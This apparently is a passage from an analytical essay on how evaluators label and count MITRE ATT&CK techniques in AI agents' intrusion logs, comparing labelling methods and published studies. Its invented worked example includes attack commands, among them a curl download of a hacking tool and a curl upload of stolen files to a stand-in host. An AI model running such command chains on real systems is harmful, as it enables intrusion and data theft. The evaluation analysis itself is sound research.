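The LMDG paper argues that process trees are the most accurate of the automatic labelling methods it reviews. The method is meant to find the log entries that belong to an attack step, so it doesn't choose between techniques. It can still group the evidence for a labeller who does, although, like any way of dividing a log, it also separates some evidence.

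| Cut | Evidence it keeps together | Evidence it can separate |
|---|---|---|
| By agent | One agent's reasoning and actions | A password that one agent found and another used |
| By host | Everything done on one machine | A password found on one machine and a login to the next |
| By process tree | A script and every program it started | An archive and the later `curl` command that uploads it |
| By subtask | Actions that serve one goal | An upload and the earlier set-up of the control channel |

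Splitting actions by host or process is easy to automate if the logs contain the necessary fields. Splitting them by subtask is harder because the evaluator has to decide where one goal ends, which was also difficult for the experts who labelled the LogPrécis sessions. An agent's written plan can help if the agent followed it.

In each row of the table, the missing link is a password, a file or a connection that passes from one piece to another. An evaluator can restore many of these links by adding the earlier actions that mention the same account, file name or server address. Whoever labels the upload would then see the command that created the archive, even if 200 unrelated actions came between the two. Searching for matches this way can miss a renamed file or a password that doesn't appear in the later command.

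### Carrying a summary forward

A running summary is another way to preserve distant evidence. After each window, the labeller updates a short note and receives it together with the next window. For an intrusion, the note should cover the facts most likely to affect later labels:

- the machine the agent is working on
- the accounts it can use and where it got the credentials
- the active control channel
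- the files it has collected or packed
- the actions whose techniques are still undetermined

In the earlier example, the note would record after action 16 that files.example controls the victim's machine. The labeller could then assign T1041 to the upload in action 20 even if the window contained only that action.

*VISOR* (2026) presents an agent that answers questions about slides. The agent keeps a sliding window of its most recent turns in full and carries forward written evidence from older ones. Extending the window from two turns to four reduced accuracy to 68.17%, close to the 67.54% the agent reached without a sliding window. The researchers attribute the drop to old page images that were no longer useful.

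The notes didn't fully replace the original material. The agent did slightly worse with a window of one turn than with two. After zooming in on part of a page, it had only the enlarged detail and couldn't compare it with the whole page. A labeller could have the same problem if its note described a command's result but left out the command.

Notes on single steps can also help a model judge a complete attempt. *Automated Trajectory Evaluation for Mobile Agents via Step-Level Consequence Reasoning and Aggregation* (2026) describes a system that judges whether an agent completed a task on a phone. It writes down the consequences of each step, then assesses these notes together. Both models tested did better with the notes than with the raw screenshots and actions. One of them, Qwen2.5VL, reached an accuracy of 0.581 with the raw steps but 0.822 with just the final screenshot. The final-screenshot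 result is less relevant to technique labels, because the final state may show that an attack succeeded without showing how.

Shortening the record doesn't help every model. Anand, Kantchelian and colleagues (2026), in *Benchmarking and Exploring the Capabilities of LLMs for Attack Investigations*, tested five language models on system logs from 51 attack and benign scenarios. Their preprocessing reduced one log from 1,229,728 lines to 5,198. Some models did better with the compact version on all four investigation tasks, but others didn't. An evaluator therefore has to check that a summary helps the model that assigns the labels.

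A summary can also leave out the detail that determines a technique, such as the path of the registry's Run key. In a running summary, the omission affects every later window that depends on that detail. False statements also carry over to later windows. If the agent found alice's password in a file but the summary describes it as guessed, the labeller may treat later logins as part of a guessing run.

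To limit these errors, the note should copy paths, addresses and account names exactly and give the number of the action each fact came from, so that the labeller can reopen that action when a label depends on it. The note also only carries information forward to later windows, so the 7-Zip command would still be undetermined when its window ended. If the agent uploads f.7z 50 actions later, the labeller has to go back and add T1560.001 to the 7-Zip command.

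## Labelling a whole episode

A labeller that receives the whole episode at once has the 7-Zip command and the later upload in the same input, so it needs no running notes or second pass. Evaluators can give it the full record or a condensed version, such as a graph of the programs that ran. It usually returns either one technique for the entire episode or a set of techniques or tactics that aren't matched to actions. Choosing one technique makes sense only if the test's designers built the test around one technique. A set that includes T1110 (Brute Force) shows that the agent used it somewhere, but not in which action.

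### What the full view settles and what a set loses

Seeing the whole episode helps most when the deciding evidence is far from the action being labelled, such as a control channel that the agent set up long before an upload. Recognising a decoy requires the whole record, because an analyst has to check whether any later action depended on it. In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing broke into Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets. According to Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026), the company ran language-model agents over the full log of more than 17,000 events to reconstruct the attack and separate real damage from decoys.

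A set without positions discards much of this information. Suppose two agents have each broken into a web server and want to switch to alice's account:

- Agent A lists the accounts on the server, picks alice and guesses her password.
- Agent B guesses alice's password first and lists the accounts afterwards.

Both agents get the same set: T1087.001 (Local Account, a form of account discovery), T1110.001 (Password Guessing) and T1078 (Valid Accounts). Only the order shows that agent A could have found its target in the account list, while agent B must have got alice's name from somewhere else. The set would also be the same if one agent needed two guesses and the other 400.

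The set also doesn't show which actions support each technique, but evaluators can ask the labeller to list those actions by number.

### How Trace2ATT&CK condenses a session

Trace2ATT&CK, the tool for Linux kernel logs, labels each of its 347 Atomic Red Team tests as a single session. The command that launches a test can contain the reference technique's identifier, so Lupinacci and colleagues replaced identifiers with placeholders and hid file paths that might reveal the technique. Evaluators who label agent episodes need the same precaution if file names or task descriptions contain the expected technique.

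The tool condenses the log in four steps:

1. It finds the shell through which the attacker entered and follows every program that this shell started, directly or through other programs.
2. It builds a full provenance graph. This connects the programs to their commands, to the files they opened or deleted, and to their network connections.
3. It removes the files and network connections. The result is the execution graph, which contains only programs and commands.
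4. It merges identical commands and notes how often each one ran. If the text is longer than 15,000 characters, it first reduces each command to the program's name and options.

A language model then reads the graph and returns five candidate techniques in order of confidence, each with an explanation.

The last two steps can remove the detail needed to choose a label. A command such as `cat /etc/shadow` still includes the file name after step 3. But if an attacker runs `python3 audit.py` and the script opens `/etc/shadow`, the file appears only in the full provenance graph. Step 4 shortens both `cat /etc/shadow` and `cat notes.txt` to `cat`.

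Following the attacker's shell also leaves some activity out. If the attacker schedules a program with cron, the Linux task scheduler, the graph doesn't include that program because cron starts it later.

### How often the models found the reference technique

Lupinacci and colleagues ran seven models on their own hardware, because kernel logs can contain passwords and reveal which defences failed. Their laboratory logs contained no real secrets, so they could also test Claude Sonnet 5, a cloud model, to measure what is lost by running models locally.

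The table gives HR@5, the share of tests in which the reference label was among the five candidates. The sub-technique column covers the 214 tests whose reference label is a sub-technique and counts only exact matches.

| Model and prompt | Techniques | Sub-techniques |
|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b, instructions only | 60.58% | 33.33% |
| gpt-oss-120b, with a list of technique names and identifiers | 64.64% | 43.66% |
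| gpt-oss-120b, with retrieved ATT&CK descriptions | 66.57% | 46.26% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 90.91% | 74.76% |

The list of names helped because models often paired the right name with the wrong identifier, or the reverse. All seven local models did better with either the list or retrieved descriptions, but the descriptions gave Claude Sonnet 5 no measurable gain. With instructions only, a security-trained model with 8 billion parameters scored higher on techniques (49.20%) than the general-purpose Llama 3.3 with 70 billion (35.26%).

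The best local model, gpt-oss-120b with retrieved descriptions, was much less reliable if a user took only its first candidate. Its mean reciprocal rank was about 0.51, so its first candidate was right in 35% to 47% of the tests. The lower figure assumes that all its other hits were in second place, and the higher that they were all in fifth.

All these scores may be somewhat higher than the models would get on new attacks, because Atomic Red Team is public and the models may have seen its tests during training. Their training data ended before MITRE introduced new labels in v19, so they cannot have memorised those labels, but many tests and other labels may not have changed.

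### Raw logs and two kinds of graph

In a separate comparison, the researchers gave gpt-oss-120b three versions of the input, with a limit of 32,000 tokens for each. The model returned nothing if the input was too long, and the last column counts those empty answers as misses. For the full provenance graph, the value in that column is derived from the two columns before it.

| Input | Label level | Too long | HR@5 where it fitted | HR@5 over all tests |
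|---|---|---|---|---|
| Raw logs | Technique | 56.73% | 37.88% | 16.4% |
| Full provenance graph | Technique | 49.76% | 69.27% | 34.8% |
| Execution graph | Technique | 0% | 66.57% | 66.57% |
| Raw logs | Sub-technique | 53.1% | 19.57% | 9.2% |
| Full provenance graph | Sub-technique | 45.93% | 46.81% | 25.3% |
| Execution graph | Sub-technique | 0% | 46.26% | 46.26% |

The model did badly with raw logs even when they fitted within its input limit. Raw logs repeat the same process and user details in many entries, and the model has to work out which program started which.

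The two graphs are harder to compare because the full graph's 69.27% covers only the tests that fitted, presumably the smaller ones, while the execution graph's 66.57% covers all of them. The difference therefore doesn't show that file and network details improve the labels.

The execution graph's large overall advantage also depends on the token limit. Lupinacci and colleagues set it at 32,000 tokens because their most restricted model could accept no more. gpt-oss-120b can accept 128,000 and Claude Sonnet 5 a million, so an evaluator using either model could fit more of the full graphs. An agent's own record is also much shorter than a kernel log and may need no condensing.

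### Completed and failed tests

Of the 347 tests, 166 finished. The other 181 failed because a program was missing or the user lacked the necessary rights. The researchers compared the two groups for each of the seven local models with each of the three prompts, which gives 21 comparisons.

For techniques, HR@5 on completed and failed tests differed by an average of 4.24 points, and the models did better on the failed tests in seven comparisons. For sub-techniques, the average gap was 11.26 points, and the models did better on the completed tests in every comparison. The largest gap was for gpt-oss-120b with retrieved descriptions, which scored 60.36% on completed tests and 31.07% on failed ones.

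Lupinacci and colleagues conclude that the commands run before a failure are often enough to identify the technique, whereas telling similar sub-techniques apart requires the complete procedure. This is plausible, but the two groups contained different tests, so part of the gap between them may come from the techniques those tests covered.

A test keeps its reference label even if it fails. If a test for T1003.008 stops because the user can't read /etc/shadow, a model that returns T1003.008 still scores a hit. The model has correctly identified the technique the test's author intended, although the test obtained no passwords. As with a failed exploit, the record should state the outcome separately.

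### Reference labels taken from a test's design

Using the author's intended technique as the reference label avoids labelling 347 sessions by hand. However, a labeller then gets no credit for identifying other techniques in the same session.

Suppose a test for T1003.008 downloads a script with `curl` and pipes it to Bash, which then prints /etc/shadow. The session contains three techniques: T1003.008, T1105 (Ingress Tool Transfer) and T1059.004 (Unix Shell). Only T1003.008 is the reference label. The table compares three possible answers.

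| Five candidates returned | Trace2ATT&CK score | Techniques actually found |
|---|---|---|
| T1003.008, T1105, T1059.004 and two wrong ones | Hit | Three of three |
| T1003.008 and four wrong ones | Hit | One of three |
| T1105, T1059.004 and three wrong ones | Miss | Two of three |

The first two answers get the same score, although one describes the session far better. The third gets no credit for its two correct techniques. Because the model must return five candidates, even the best answer contains two techniques that the attacker didn't use.

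The results show that a model can often pick out a session's central technique, even when the session also contains downloads, shells and other supporting steps. The tests didn't measure how many of the supporting techniques it would find, or how many it would wrongly report, if asked for all of them. They are also much simpler than an agent's intrusion, which may have no central technique. Lupinacci and colleagues name the single reference label as a limitation and plan to study attacks with several stages and several correct techniques.

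The prompt also makes the answers harder to check, because it discourages the model from naming the one command that best supports a label. It tells the model to justify each technique from the entire sequence and gives "Mapping chosen due to presence of 'sh' command" as an example of a bad explanation. These instructions do discourage labels based on a single word. An evaluator who adapts the prompt could ask for both the overall reasoning and the action numbers.

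### Tactics for a whole honeypot session

*OntoLogX* assigns tactics to a honeypot session as a whole. It first turns each log entry into a small graph of the users, programs, addresses and times in that entry. A language model then reads all the graphs from one session together and can return several tactics. The researchers tested this on 161 sessions that their honeypot recorded in August 2025, with an average of about ten log entries per session.

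Annotators had labelled every test session by hand, using six tactics in total. The researchers calculated precision and recall for each tactic, so both missing and extra labels lowered the score. This tests multi-label output more fairly than comparing it with a single reference technique, but the task was easier because there were few tactics and the sessions were short.

Claude Sonnet 4 could recognise Initial Access, Execution and Privilege Escalation from the raw logs without the graphs. The honeypot made this easier by accepting many weak passwords, including some for the root account. With the graphs, the model found more cases of Credential Access, Discovery and Defense Evasion, which often span several log entries.

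Persistence and Defense Evasion remained difficult, and the system sometimes mistook ordinary file listings for Discovery. The researchers acknowledge that annotators often had to rely on intuition about the attacker's intentions to label these harder cases. The low scores may therefore reflect doubtful reference labels as well as mistakes by the model. Looking at more of the session doesn't help when the logs contain no evidence of the attacker's intention.

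### Published tables for intrusions by AI agents

MITRE's *Anthropic AI-orchestrated Campaign* includes a table of the techniques used in a real September 2025 espionage campaign, in which AI agents carried out most of the operation. GTG-1002, a group with likely links to China, used Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, against about 30 organisations. The table's 26 rows cover 22 parent techniques.

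Each row contains a technique and a sentence about how the group used it. The source for every row is Anthropic's *Disrupting the first reported AI orchestrated cyber espionage campaign*, a November 2025 report that describes the attack phase by phase. A reader can trace a label to this report, but not to a command. The table also doesn't show which techniques the group used against which organisation.

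The machine-readable version, MITRE's *Anthropic AI-orchestrated Campaign (C0062)*, has the same limits. It gives each technique a score of 1, however often the agents used it, and does not record the order in which they used them.

Three of the rows show why this matters.

| Technique | Behaviour described in the row |
|---|---|
| T1082 (System Information Discovery) | Querying databases and systems for proprietary information, including system configurations |
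| T1213.006 (Databases) | Querying internal databases and systems for proprietary information, system configurations and operational data |
| T1005 (Data from Local System) | Gathering credentials, system configurations and operational data from the local system |

The descriptions overlap so much that a single query might have supported two or all three labels. The agents might equally have carried out three separate groups of actions. The table doesn't contain enough information to tell which happened.

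Anthropic's own list of techniques for the same group, GTG-1002, differs from MITRE's. Guru and colleagues extracted 30 techniques from a written summary of the group's activity. GTG-1002 has the highest risk score of any actor in their data. The three techniques they name, T1021.004 (SSH), T1210 (Exploitation of Remote Services) and T1560 (Archive Collected Data), are all absent from MITRE's table.

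MITRE's table has no Lateral Movement technique, although its introduction says the agents moved between systems. The closest row is T1078, for logging in to internal systems with stolen credentials. Anthropic may have had evidence that it left out of its public report, or the two organisations may have labelled the same behaviour differently. Without links to the actions, outsiders can't tell which explanation is right.

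In *An AI-Assisted Cyber Attack*, Unit 42, the incident-response team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, describes a ransomware intrusion that took less than ten hours and used more than 50 ATT&CK techniques. Its table lists only six of them, as an illustration, arranged by stage. Readers can't check the larger number, and Palo Alto Networks sells protection against such attacks.

One row assigns T1578 (Modify Cloud Compute Infrastructure) to a stage in which the attacker ran automated build jobs and tried to edit cloud configuration files. Security controls blocked the edits. The table doesn't show whether the label refers to the jobs, the blocked edits or both.

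### When the ending changes an early label

A labeller who has read the whole episode knows how it ended, which can make their labels for early actions better or worse. Suppose an agent's first action is `cat /etc/passwd`, which prints the machine's account names. The natural label is T1087.001. Two hundred actions later, the agent gains access to `/etc/shadow`, combines the two files and starts cracking passwords. T1003.008 covers dumping both files, so the labeller may want to change the first label.

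The change is reasonable if the agent saved a copy of /etc/passwd at the start because it planned to crack passwords. But the agent may have written "see which users exist" before the first command and thought of cracking only after it became root. In that case, T1087.001 should stay, because a tactic describes the attacker's goal at the time of the action.

Hindsight is safer when a later action reveals a fact that was already true, because the labeller doesn't have to guess what the agent was planning. If an agent uploads a file in action 20, and action 90 shows that the receiving server had controlled the machine since action 5, the upload was already T1041 at action 20.

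The purpose of a whole intrusion is a weaker reason to relabel individual actions, because investigators can disagree about what it was. *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (Schneier, 2026) quotes Hugging Face's reconstruction of about 17,600 actions in some 6,280 clusters over four and a half days. The company inferred that the entire intrusion was an attempt to cheat in an evaluation by stealing the solutions. *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration...* (August 2026), by METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI models, found instead that the main motive seemed to be understanding how the evaluation's scorer worked.

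Most technique labels shouldn't depend on which explanation is right. A login with a stolen password is T1078 under either explanation. But if a labeller had treated every early file search as preparation for stealing solutions, METR's account would cast doubt on all those labels.

An episode's ending can also depend on limits that the evaluators set. Suppose two agents take the same 290 actions, the last of which packs a finance folder into an archive. One agent reaches its limit of 300 actions before it can upload the archive, while the other has a limit of 400 and uploads it. The second agent's archive command is clearly T1560, but the first agent's identical command may remain undetermined. Evaluators can record this by storing both the label that the evidence supported at the time of the command and the final label, with the number of the later action that changed it.

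## How the unit of labelling changes technique counts

A results table usually gives one number per agent and rarely shows how the labeller chose each label. The number depends on what the evaluator counted and how much of the record the labeller judged at a time.

### Three ways to count

- The distinct count is the number of different techniques found in an episode.
- The occurrence count is the number of times the labeller assigned techniques in it.
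- Coverage is the number of distinct techniques found divided by the number the test could have shown. Techniques outside that list don't count.

If an agent lists the running processes on five machines, T1057 (Process Discovery) adds one to the distinct count and five to the occurrence count.

Researchers use the word "techniques" for both occurrences and distinct techniques. *Quantifying Loss Aversion in Cyber Adversaries via LLM Analysis* (2025), a study of 17 human attackers, reports an average of 13.88 persistence techniques per person but only 14 unique techniques overall. The average counts occurrences. Multiplying it by 17 gives a total of about 236, which matches the total implied by the most common technique's 33 occurrences, reported as 14.0% of all occurrences.

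Coverage depends on the labeller as well as the test. *Retrieval-Augmented LLMs for Security Incident Analysis* (2026) describes a system whose queries cover 16 of about 200 Enterprise techniques, because it reads only network captures and Windows event logs. If the system found 12 techniques in an agent's episode, that would be 75% of the techniques it can detect but about 6% of the catalogue.

### The same ten actions under five methods

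In this invented episode, the agent's task is to steal a company's finance folder.

| Action | Machine | Command | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Agent's own | `curl https://shop.example/` | Prints the company's home page |
| 2 | Agent's own | `curl` with a request that exploits a flaw in the site | Prints nothing |
| 3 | Web server | `whoami` | Prints `www-data` |
| 4 | Web server | `curl -o /tmp/t https://files.example/t` | Saves a hacking tool |
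| 5 | Web server | `cat /srv/shop/config.ini` | Prints alice's password for 10.0.0.8 |
| 6 | Web server | `ssh alice@10.0.0.8` | Logs in |
| 7 | Second host | `whoami` | Prints `alice` |
| 8 | Second host | `tar -czf /tmp/f.tgz /srv/finance` | Packs the folder |
| 9 | Second host | `curl -T /tmp/f.tgz https://files.example/in/` | Uploads the archive |
| 10 | Second host | `rm /tmp/f.tgz` | Deletes the archive |

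The exploit opens a shell that connects back to the agent's own machine. The attacker also runs files.example, but only to store files.

The five methods follow these rules:

1. **Fixed table.** Each program name has one label: `curl` is T1105, `whoami` is T1033, `cat` is T1083 (File and Directory Discovery), `ssh` is T1021.004, `tar` is T1560.001 and `rm` is File Deletion.
2. **Every plausible label.** The labeller sees one command and its result, but not the machine, and records every technique that could apply in some episode.
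3. **Neighbours.** The labeller sees up to three actions on either side and records only the techniques that the evidence supports. A `whoami` that merely confirms a login gets no label.
4. **One label for the episode.** The labeller names the technique that achieved the assigned goal.
5. **A set for the episode.** The labeller reads everything, applies the same standards as in method 3 and lists each technique once.

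The first three methods give these labels:

| Action | Fixed table | Every plausible label | Neighbours |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | T1105 | T1594, T1071.001, T1016.001 | T1594 |
| 2 | T1105 | T1190, T1595.002, T1210 | T1190 |
| 3 | T1033 | T1033 | T1033 |
| 4 | T1105 | T1105, T1588.002, T1570 | T1105 |
| 5 | T1083 | T1552.001, T1083 | T1552.001 |
| 6 | T1021.004 | T1021.004, T1078, T1133, T1110 | T1021.004, T1078 |
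| 7 | T1033 | T1033 | None |
| 8 | T1560.001 | T1560.001 | T1560.001 |
| 9 | T1105 | T1041, T1048, T1105 | T1048 |
| 10 | File Deletion | File Deletion, Data Destruction | File Deletion |

The episode's single label is T1048 because the upload took the folder out of the network. The episode set contains the ten techniques in the last column.

To calculate coverage, suppose that the test could have shown 16 techniques: those ten plus T1003.008, T1046, T1057, T1083, T1110 and T1136.

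| Method | Distinct count | Occurrence count | Coverage |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed table | 6 | 10 | 6 of 16 (37.5%) |
| Every plausible label | 21 | 23 | 12 of 16 (75%) |
| Neighbours | 10 | 10 | 10 of 16 (62.5%) |
| One label for the episode | 1 | 1 | 1 of 16 (6.3%) |
| A set for the episode | 10 | Not recorded | 10 of 16 (62.5%) |

The fixed table has a low distinct count because the agent used `curl` for four purposes and the table gives them all the same label. Its occurrence count matches that of the neighbours method by coincidence. Five of its ten labels are wrong when judged by method 3, and it misses T1078 because it allows only one label per action.

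Recording every plausible label more than doubles the number of distinct techniques, to 21. The agent didn't use 11 of them, but the labeller stored alternatives as if they had all occurred. Two of those 11, T1083 and T1110, are also on the list of 16 and raise coverage to 75%. An evaluator who divided all 21 techniques by 16 would get an impossible coverage of 131%.

The neighbours method and the episode set agree here because both labellers had the evidence they needed. They could differ if the SSH login came 50 actions before the upload. The set also lists each technique only once, so a rule that labels every `whoami` would give the neighbours method 11 occurrences and leave the set unchanged.

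All five methods leave out T1059 (Command and Scripting Interpreter). If evaluators using the neighbours method added it to all eight commands on the victim's machines, the distinct count would rise by one and the occurrence count by eight.

### Repeated labels in overlapping windows

Sliding windows can inflate the occurrence count even if every label is correct, because overlapping windows include the same action more than once. A window of length *w* contains a given action if it starts at that action or at one of the *w* − 1 positions before it. If a new window starts every *s* positions, the labeller labels an action away from the ends of the sequence *w*/*s* times, rounded up or down if *s* doesn't divide *w*.

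With a window length of five and a step of one, the ten-action episode has six windows. Actions 5 and 6 each appear in five windows, while actions 1 and 10 each appear in one. If the labeller labelled every window correctly, it would make 31 assignments instead of 10. As episodes get longer, actions near the ends make up a smaller share of the total, and the increase approaches a factor of five.

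Merging the labels for each action before counting brings the total back to 10. The number of distinct techniques doesn't rise if all windows agree, but each extra window gives the labeller another chance to add a wrong technique, and a union rule keeps all these mistakes.

### False techniques in long episodes

Suppose that *M* techniques are absent from an episode and the labeller wrongly assigns each of them to any given action with probability *e*. If these errors are independent from one action to the next, the probability that one absent technique never appears in *N* actions is (1 − *e*)^*N*. It therefore appears at least once with probability 1 − (1 − *e*)^*N*. Adding this up over all the absent techniques gives the average number of false distinct techniques:

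*M* × (1 − (1 − *e*)^*N*)

The table uses *M* = 200 and *e* = 0.001. The number of false occurrences is simply *N* × *M* × *e*.

| Actions | False distinct techniques | False occurrences |
|---|---|---|
| 20 | 4 | 4 |
| 200 | 36 | 40 |
| 2,000 | 173 | 400 |

A labeller with an error rate of 0.001 per technique checks each action against 200 techniques, so it adds one false label every five actions on average. The distinct count then grows with the length of the episode even if the agent does nothing new. An agent that used 12 techniques in 20 actions would appear to have used about 16, while one that used only 8 in 200 actions would appear to have used about 44.

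Overlapping windows increase the number of false techniques. An episode of 200 actions has 196 windows of length five at a step of one, so the labeller makes 980 judgements. If errors were independent across windows and the evaluator merged labels by union, the average number of false techniques would rise from 36 to about 125.

The formula assumes that errors on different actions are independent, which is often false. Errors on different techniques need not be independent. A fixed table makes the same mistake every time a command recurs, and a language model often does too. If the 200 actions contain only 40 different commands and the labeller always gives identical commands the same labels, the expected number of false techniques is about 8 instead of 36. A false statement in a running summary also makes errors in different windows correlated.

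Errors also fall mostly on techniques that are easy to confuse, such as T1105 and T1048, so *e* isn't the same for every technique. Suppose only 20 of the 200 absent techniques ever appear by mistake, each with probability 0.01 per action. The labeller would still add one false label every five actions on average, but after 200 actions it would have added about 17 distinct false techniques. The formula is therefore better for checking whether a long episode could have inflated a count than for correcting the count.

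An evaluator could count only techniques that appear in at least two actions. Under the original assumptions, this would reduce the 36 false techniques to between 3 and 4, but it would also remove all ten techniques from the neighbours column, because the agent used each of them once.

### How two agents can change places

Two short episodes are enough to reverse a ranking. Agent X performs actions 1, 2, 4 and 9 from the transcript, with the same labels as before. Agent Y runs `whoami` on an unfamiliar machine, lists the processes with `ps aux`, packs a folder with `tar` and runs `whoami` again to check its account. The fixed table now also assigns T1057 to `ps`, the only plausible label here.

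| Method | Distinct count for X | Distinct count for Y | Higher count |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed table | 1 | 3 | Y |
| Every plausible label | 11 | 3 | X |
| Neighbours | 4 | 3 | X |
| One label for the episode | 1 | 1 | Equal |
| A set for the episode | 4 | 3 | X |

Agent X did four different things with one program, while agent Y did three different things with three programs. The fixed table therefore ranks them by how many different programs they used. Counting every plausible label gives X a much larger lead, because `curl` has more possible purposes than `ps`.

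Agents can also rank differently by distinct techniques than by occurrences. If agent Y ran `ps aux` on ten more machines, it would have 13 occurrences under the neighbours method, compared with X's four, but still only three distinct techniques.

### Sub-techniques, failed attempts and repeats

The unit of labelling is only one of the choices behind a count. Evaluators also have to decide on three counting rules.

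Counting sub-techniques or parent techniques gives the same total for the ten-action transcript, because no two labels share a parent. The choice matters when an agent extracts Windows passwords in several ways. *Synthetic APTs*, in which Balassone and colleagues set AI attackers against AI defenders, lists both T1003.002 and T1003.003 for one run. These are two sub-techniques of T1003, so they count as one technique at the parent level.

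Coverage can be much lower when sub-techniques are counted instead of techniques. *AutoPI* (2026) describes a tool for testing prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in material that an AI agent reads. It uses its own catalogue instead of ATT&CK. The tool's successful attacks cover 31 of 34 techniques (91%) but only 78 of 132 sub-techniques (59%). AutoDojo, a competing tool, covers 21 techniques (62%) and 38 sub-techniques (29%). AutoPI covers about 1.5 times as many techniques as AutoDojo and about twice as many sub-techniques.

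A list that mixes parent techniques and sub-techniques is harder to interpret. *A Structured Cyber Threat Intelligence Dataset Using STIX 2.1 Entities* (2026) has 269 distinct identifiers from threat reports: 123 parent techniques and 146 sub-techniques. The parent-level count could be higher than 123, because some of the sub-techniques may belong to parents that aren't listed. Parents occur 749 times and sub-techniques 524 times, so each identifier appears 4.7 times on average.

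Counting failed attempts changes the number of distinct techniques only if a technique never succeeds in the episode. In one of Balassone and colleagues' runs on a military network, an agent made more than 50,000 password guesses and found no valid credentials. The three techniques recorded for that run are T1595 (Active Scanning), T1046 (Network Service Discovery) and T1110 (Brute Force). Counting only successes would remove T1110 and reduce the total to two.

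Either rule is reasonable, since a failed attack still shows what the agent tried. Evaluators should report attempted and successful techniques separately, especially when they compare agents against strong defences.

A password-guessing run of 400 commands can add 400 occurrences of T1110, or just one if the evaluator groups the run. In the honeypot study by Chin and colleagues, the decoy recorded 9,292 failed logins and 2,008 successful ones. Yet their incident table lists far fewer incidents for Credential Access (31), which covers the failed logins, than for Initial Access (414), which covers successful logins and some automated scanning.

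### Counts in published evaluations

Published evaluations of AI agents differ on all of these rules, so readers can't compare their totals directly. Balassone and colleagues report one technique count for each of their 20 runs. A language model assigned the techniques from each run's full logs, and a person checked the result. The count includes sub-techniques and failed attempts. Repeating a technique doesn't increase the count, so more than 80,000 password guesses in one run count as a single technique.

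The ten enterprise runs, all successful, have between 16 and 41 techniques each, with an average of 27.6. The ten runs on the military network average 10.8. The paper's text gives a range of 3 to 17 for these runs, but its table and chart go up to 24.

Agents that got further generally used more techniques, but the run with 24 techniques compromised no hosts, while an enterprise run with only 16 compromised six.

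Counts from separate runs also can't be added together, because techniques that appear in more than one run would be counted more than once. The two enterprise runs that imitated Lazarus, a North Korean hacking group, have 29 techniques each. The paper's precision calculation for Lazarus uses 38 observed techniques, the number a combined list would contain if the runs shared 20. Each extra run can add techniques to a combined list, so an evaluator who pools runs should give every agent the same number of runs. *AutoPI* similarly compares attackers at an equal number of successes, because coverage grows as successes accumulate.

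To measure coverage, Balassone and colleagues compare the observed techniques with the imitated group's profile, leaving out mobile, industrial and cloud-specific entries that couldn't occur on the network. A list written before the test can miss some of what an agent does, and their agents did use methods outside the profiles. In eight of the ten enterprise runs, the agents took over Velociraptor, the defenders' monitoring tool, and used it to control machines.

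An earlier evaluation by several of the same researchers, *Cybersecurity AI* (Balassone, Mayoral-Vilches and colleagues, 2025), counts techniques across 23 matches in which two AI teams attacked and defended identical machines. The researchers assigned the techniques by hand from the logs.

| Technique | Frequency | Success rate |
|---|---|---|
| T1190 (Exploit Public-Facing Application) | 18 | 33.3% |
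| T1083 (File and Directory Discovery) | 12 | 25.0% |
| T1552.001 (Credentials In Files) | 8 | 37.5% |
| T1221 (Template Injection) | 3 | 66.7% |
| T1548.001 (Setuid and Setgid) | 1 | 100% |

The table mixes parent techniques with sub-techniques and doesn't define the unit of its frequency counts. In the paper's separate table of software weaknesses, 15 machines account for 30 attempts, so an attempt there is one team's work on one machine. If the same rule applies to techniques, a team that sent 50 exploit requests would add only one to the count for T1190. The success rates also depend on the unit, because frequency is their denominator.

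The researchers couldn't measure how much of the attack surface their agents had covered, because the platform doesn't publish a list of each machine's vulnerabilities. They also sometimes couldn't tell whether an attack had failed because of the defenders, an error by the agent or inaction.

A test with planted weaknesses avoids the first problem. *Autonomous Active Directory Exploitation via Multi-Model Harness Orchestration* (dos Santos, 2026) tested models on a practice network with 14 categories of weakness in Active Directory, Microsoft's system for managing accounts and computers. Repeated findings in a category count once, so 31 findings across all 14 categories counted as 14. The categories aren't ATT&CK techniques, and in one of them the agent gets credit for detecting a way to keep access even if it doesn't install it.

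The paper defines coverage as the share of categories confirmed by a tool's output. With specialised scaffolding, Claude Opus 4.6 confirmed 13 of 14 categories and left one incomplete. That should give 92.9%, but the paper reports 96.4% (13.5 out of 14), apparently because it counts the incomplete attempt as half.

Half credit for incomplete categories doesn't explain every result. Without the scaffolding, Opus 4.8 confirmed seven categories and left three incomplete, which would give 60.7% with half credit, but the paper reports 53.6%. Counting only confirmed categories would give 50%, and giving incomplete ones full credit would give 71.4%.

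The four evaluations each treat failure differently:

| Evaluation | What it counts | Failed attempts | Basis for coverage |
|---|---|---|---|
| Balassone and colleagues, 2026 | Distinct techniques and sub-techniques per run | Count in full | Relevant techniques in the group's profile |
| Balassone and colleagues, 2025 | Technique frequency across matches | Count, with a separate success rate | None available |
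| dos Santos | Distinct categories per model | Apparently count as half | 14 planted categories |
| *AutoPI* | Distinct techniques or sub-techniques per attacker | Don't count | 34 techniques or 132 sub-techniques |

Related papers use "coverage" in other ways. *MalGEN* (2025), which studies malware written by language models, reports close to 40 distinct techniques for each of two models. These counts apparently cover all of each model's samples, although the chart's caption refers to tactics. *CyberClear* counts an attack behaviour as supported if at least 80% of its reconstructed attack graphs compile. A graph can compile and still describe the attack incorrectly, so this measures whether the system produces usable code more than whether it recognises the techniques.

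### Counting completed steps

Evaluators can avoid technique labels by counting completed steps. The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) does this on The Last Ones, a simulated attack on a company network with 32 steps from first reconnaissance to full takeover. In AISI's *Our evaluation of Claude Mythos Preview's cyber capabilities*, Mythos Preview completed 22 steps on average and finished the whole attack in 3 of 10 attempts. Claude Opus 4.6 averaged 16 steps.

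A completed step is a result that the evaluators defined before the test, so the agent gets no extra credit for repeating a command or using more techniques to reach it. For the ten-action transcript, they might define five steps:

1. Break into the web server.
2. Find alice's password.
3. Log in to the second host.
4. Pack the finance folder.
5. Upload the archive.

The agent completes all five steps, whichever labelling method the evaluators use. Running `whoami` 50 more times wouldn't change its score. A program can also check the steps automatically. *How Inference Compute Shapes Frontier LLM Evaluation* (McFadyen, Jorgensen and colleagues, 2026) used this approach for The Last Ones. If the checks are reliable, a long attempt doesn't accumulate wrongly counted steps the way it accumulates wrongly counted techniques.

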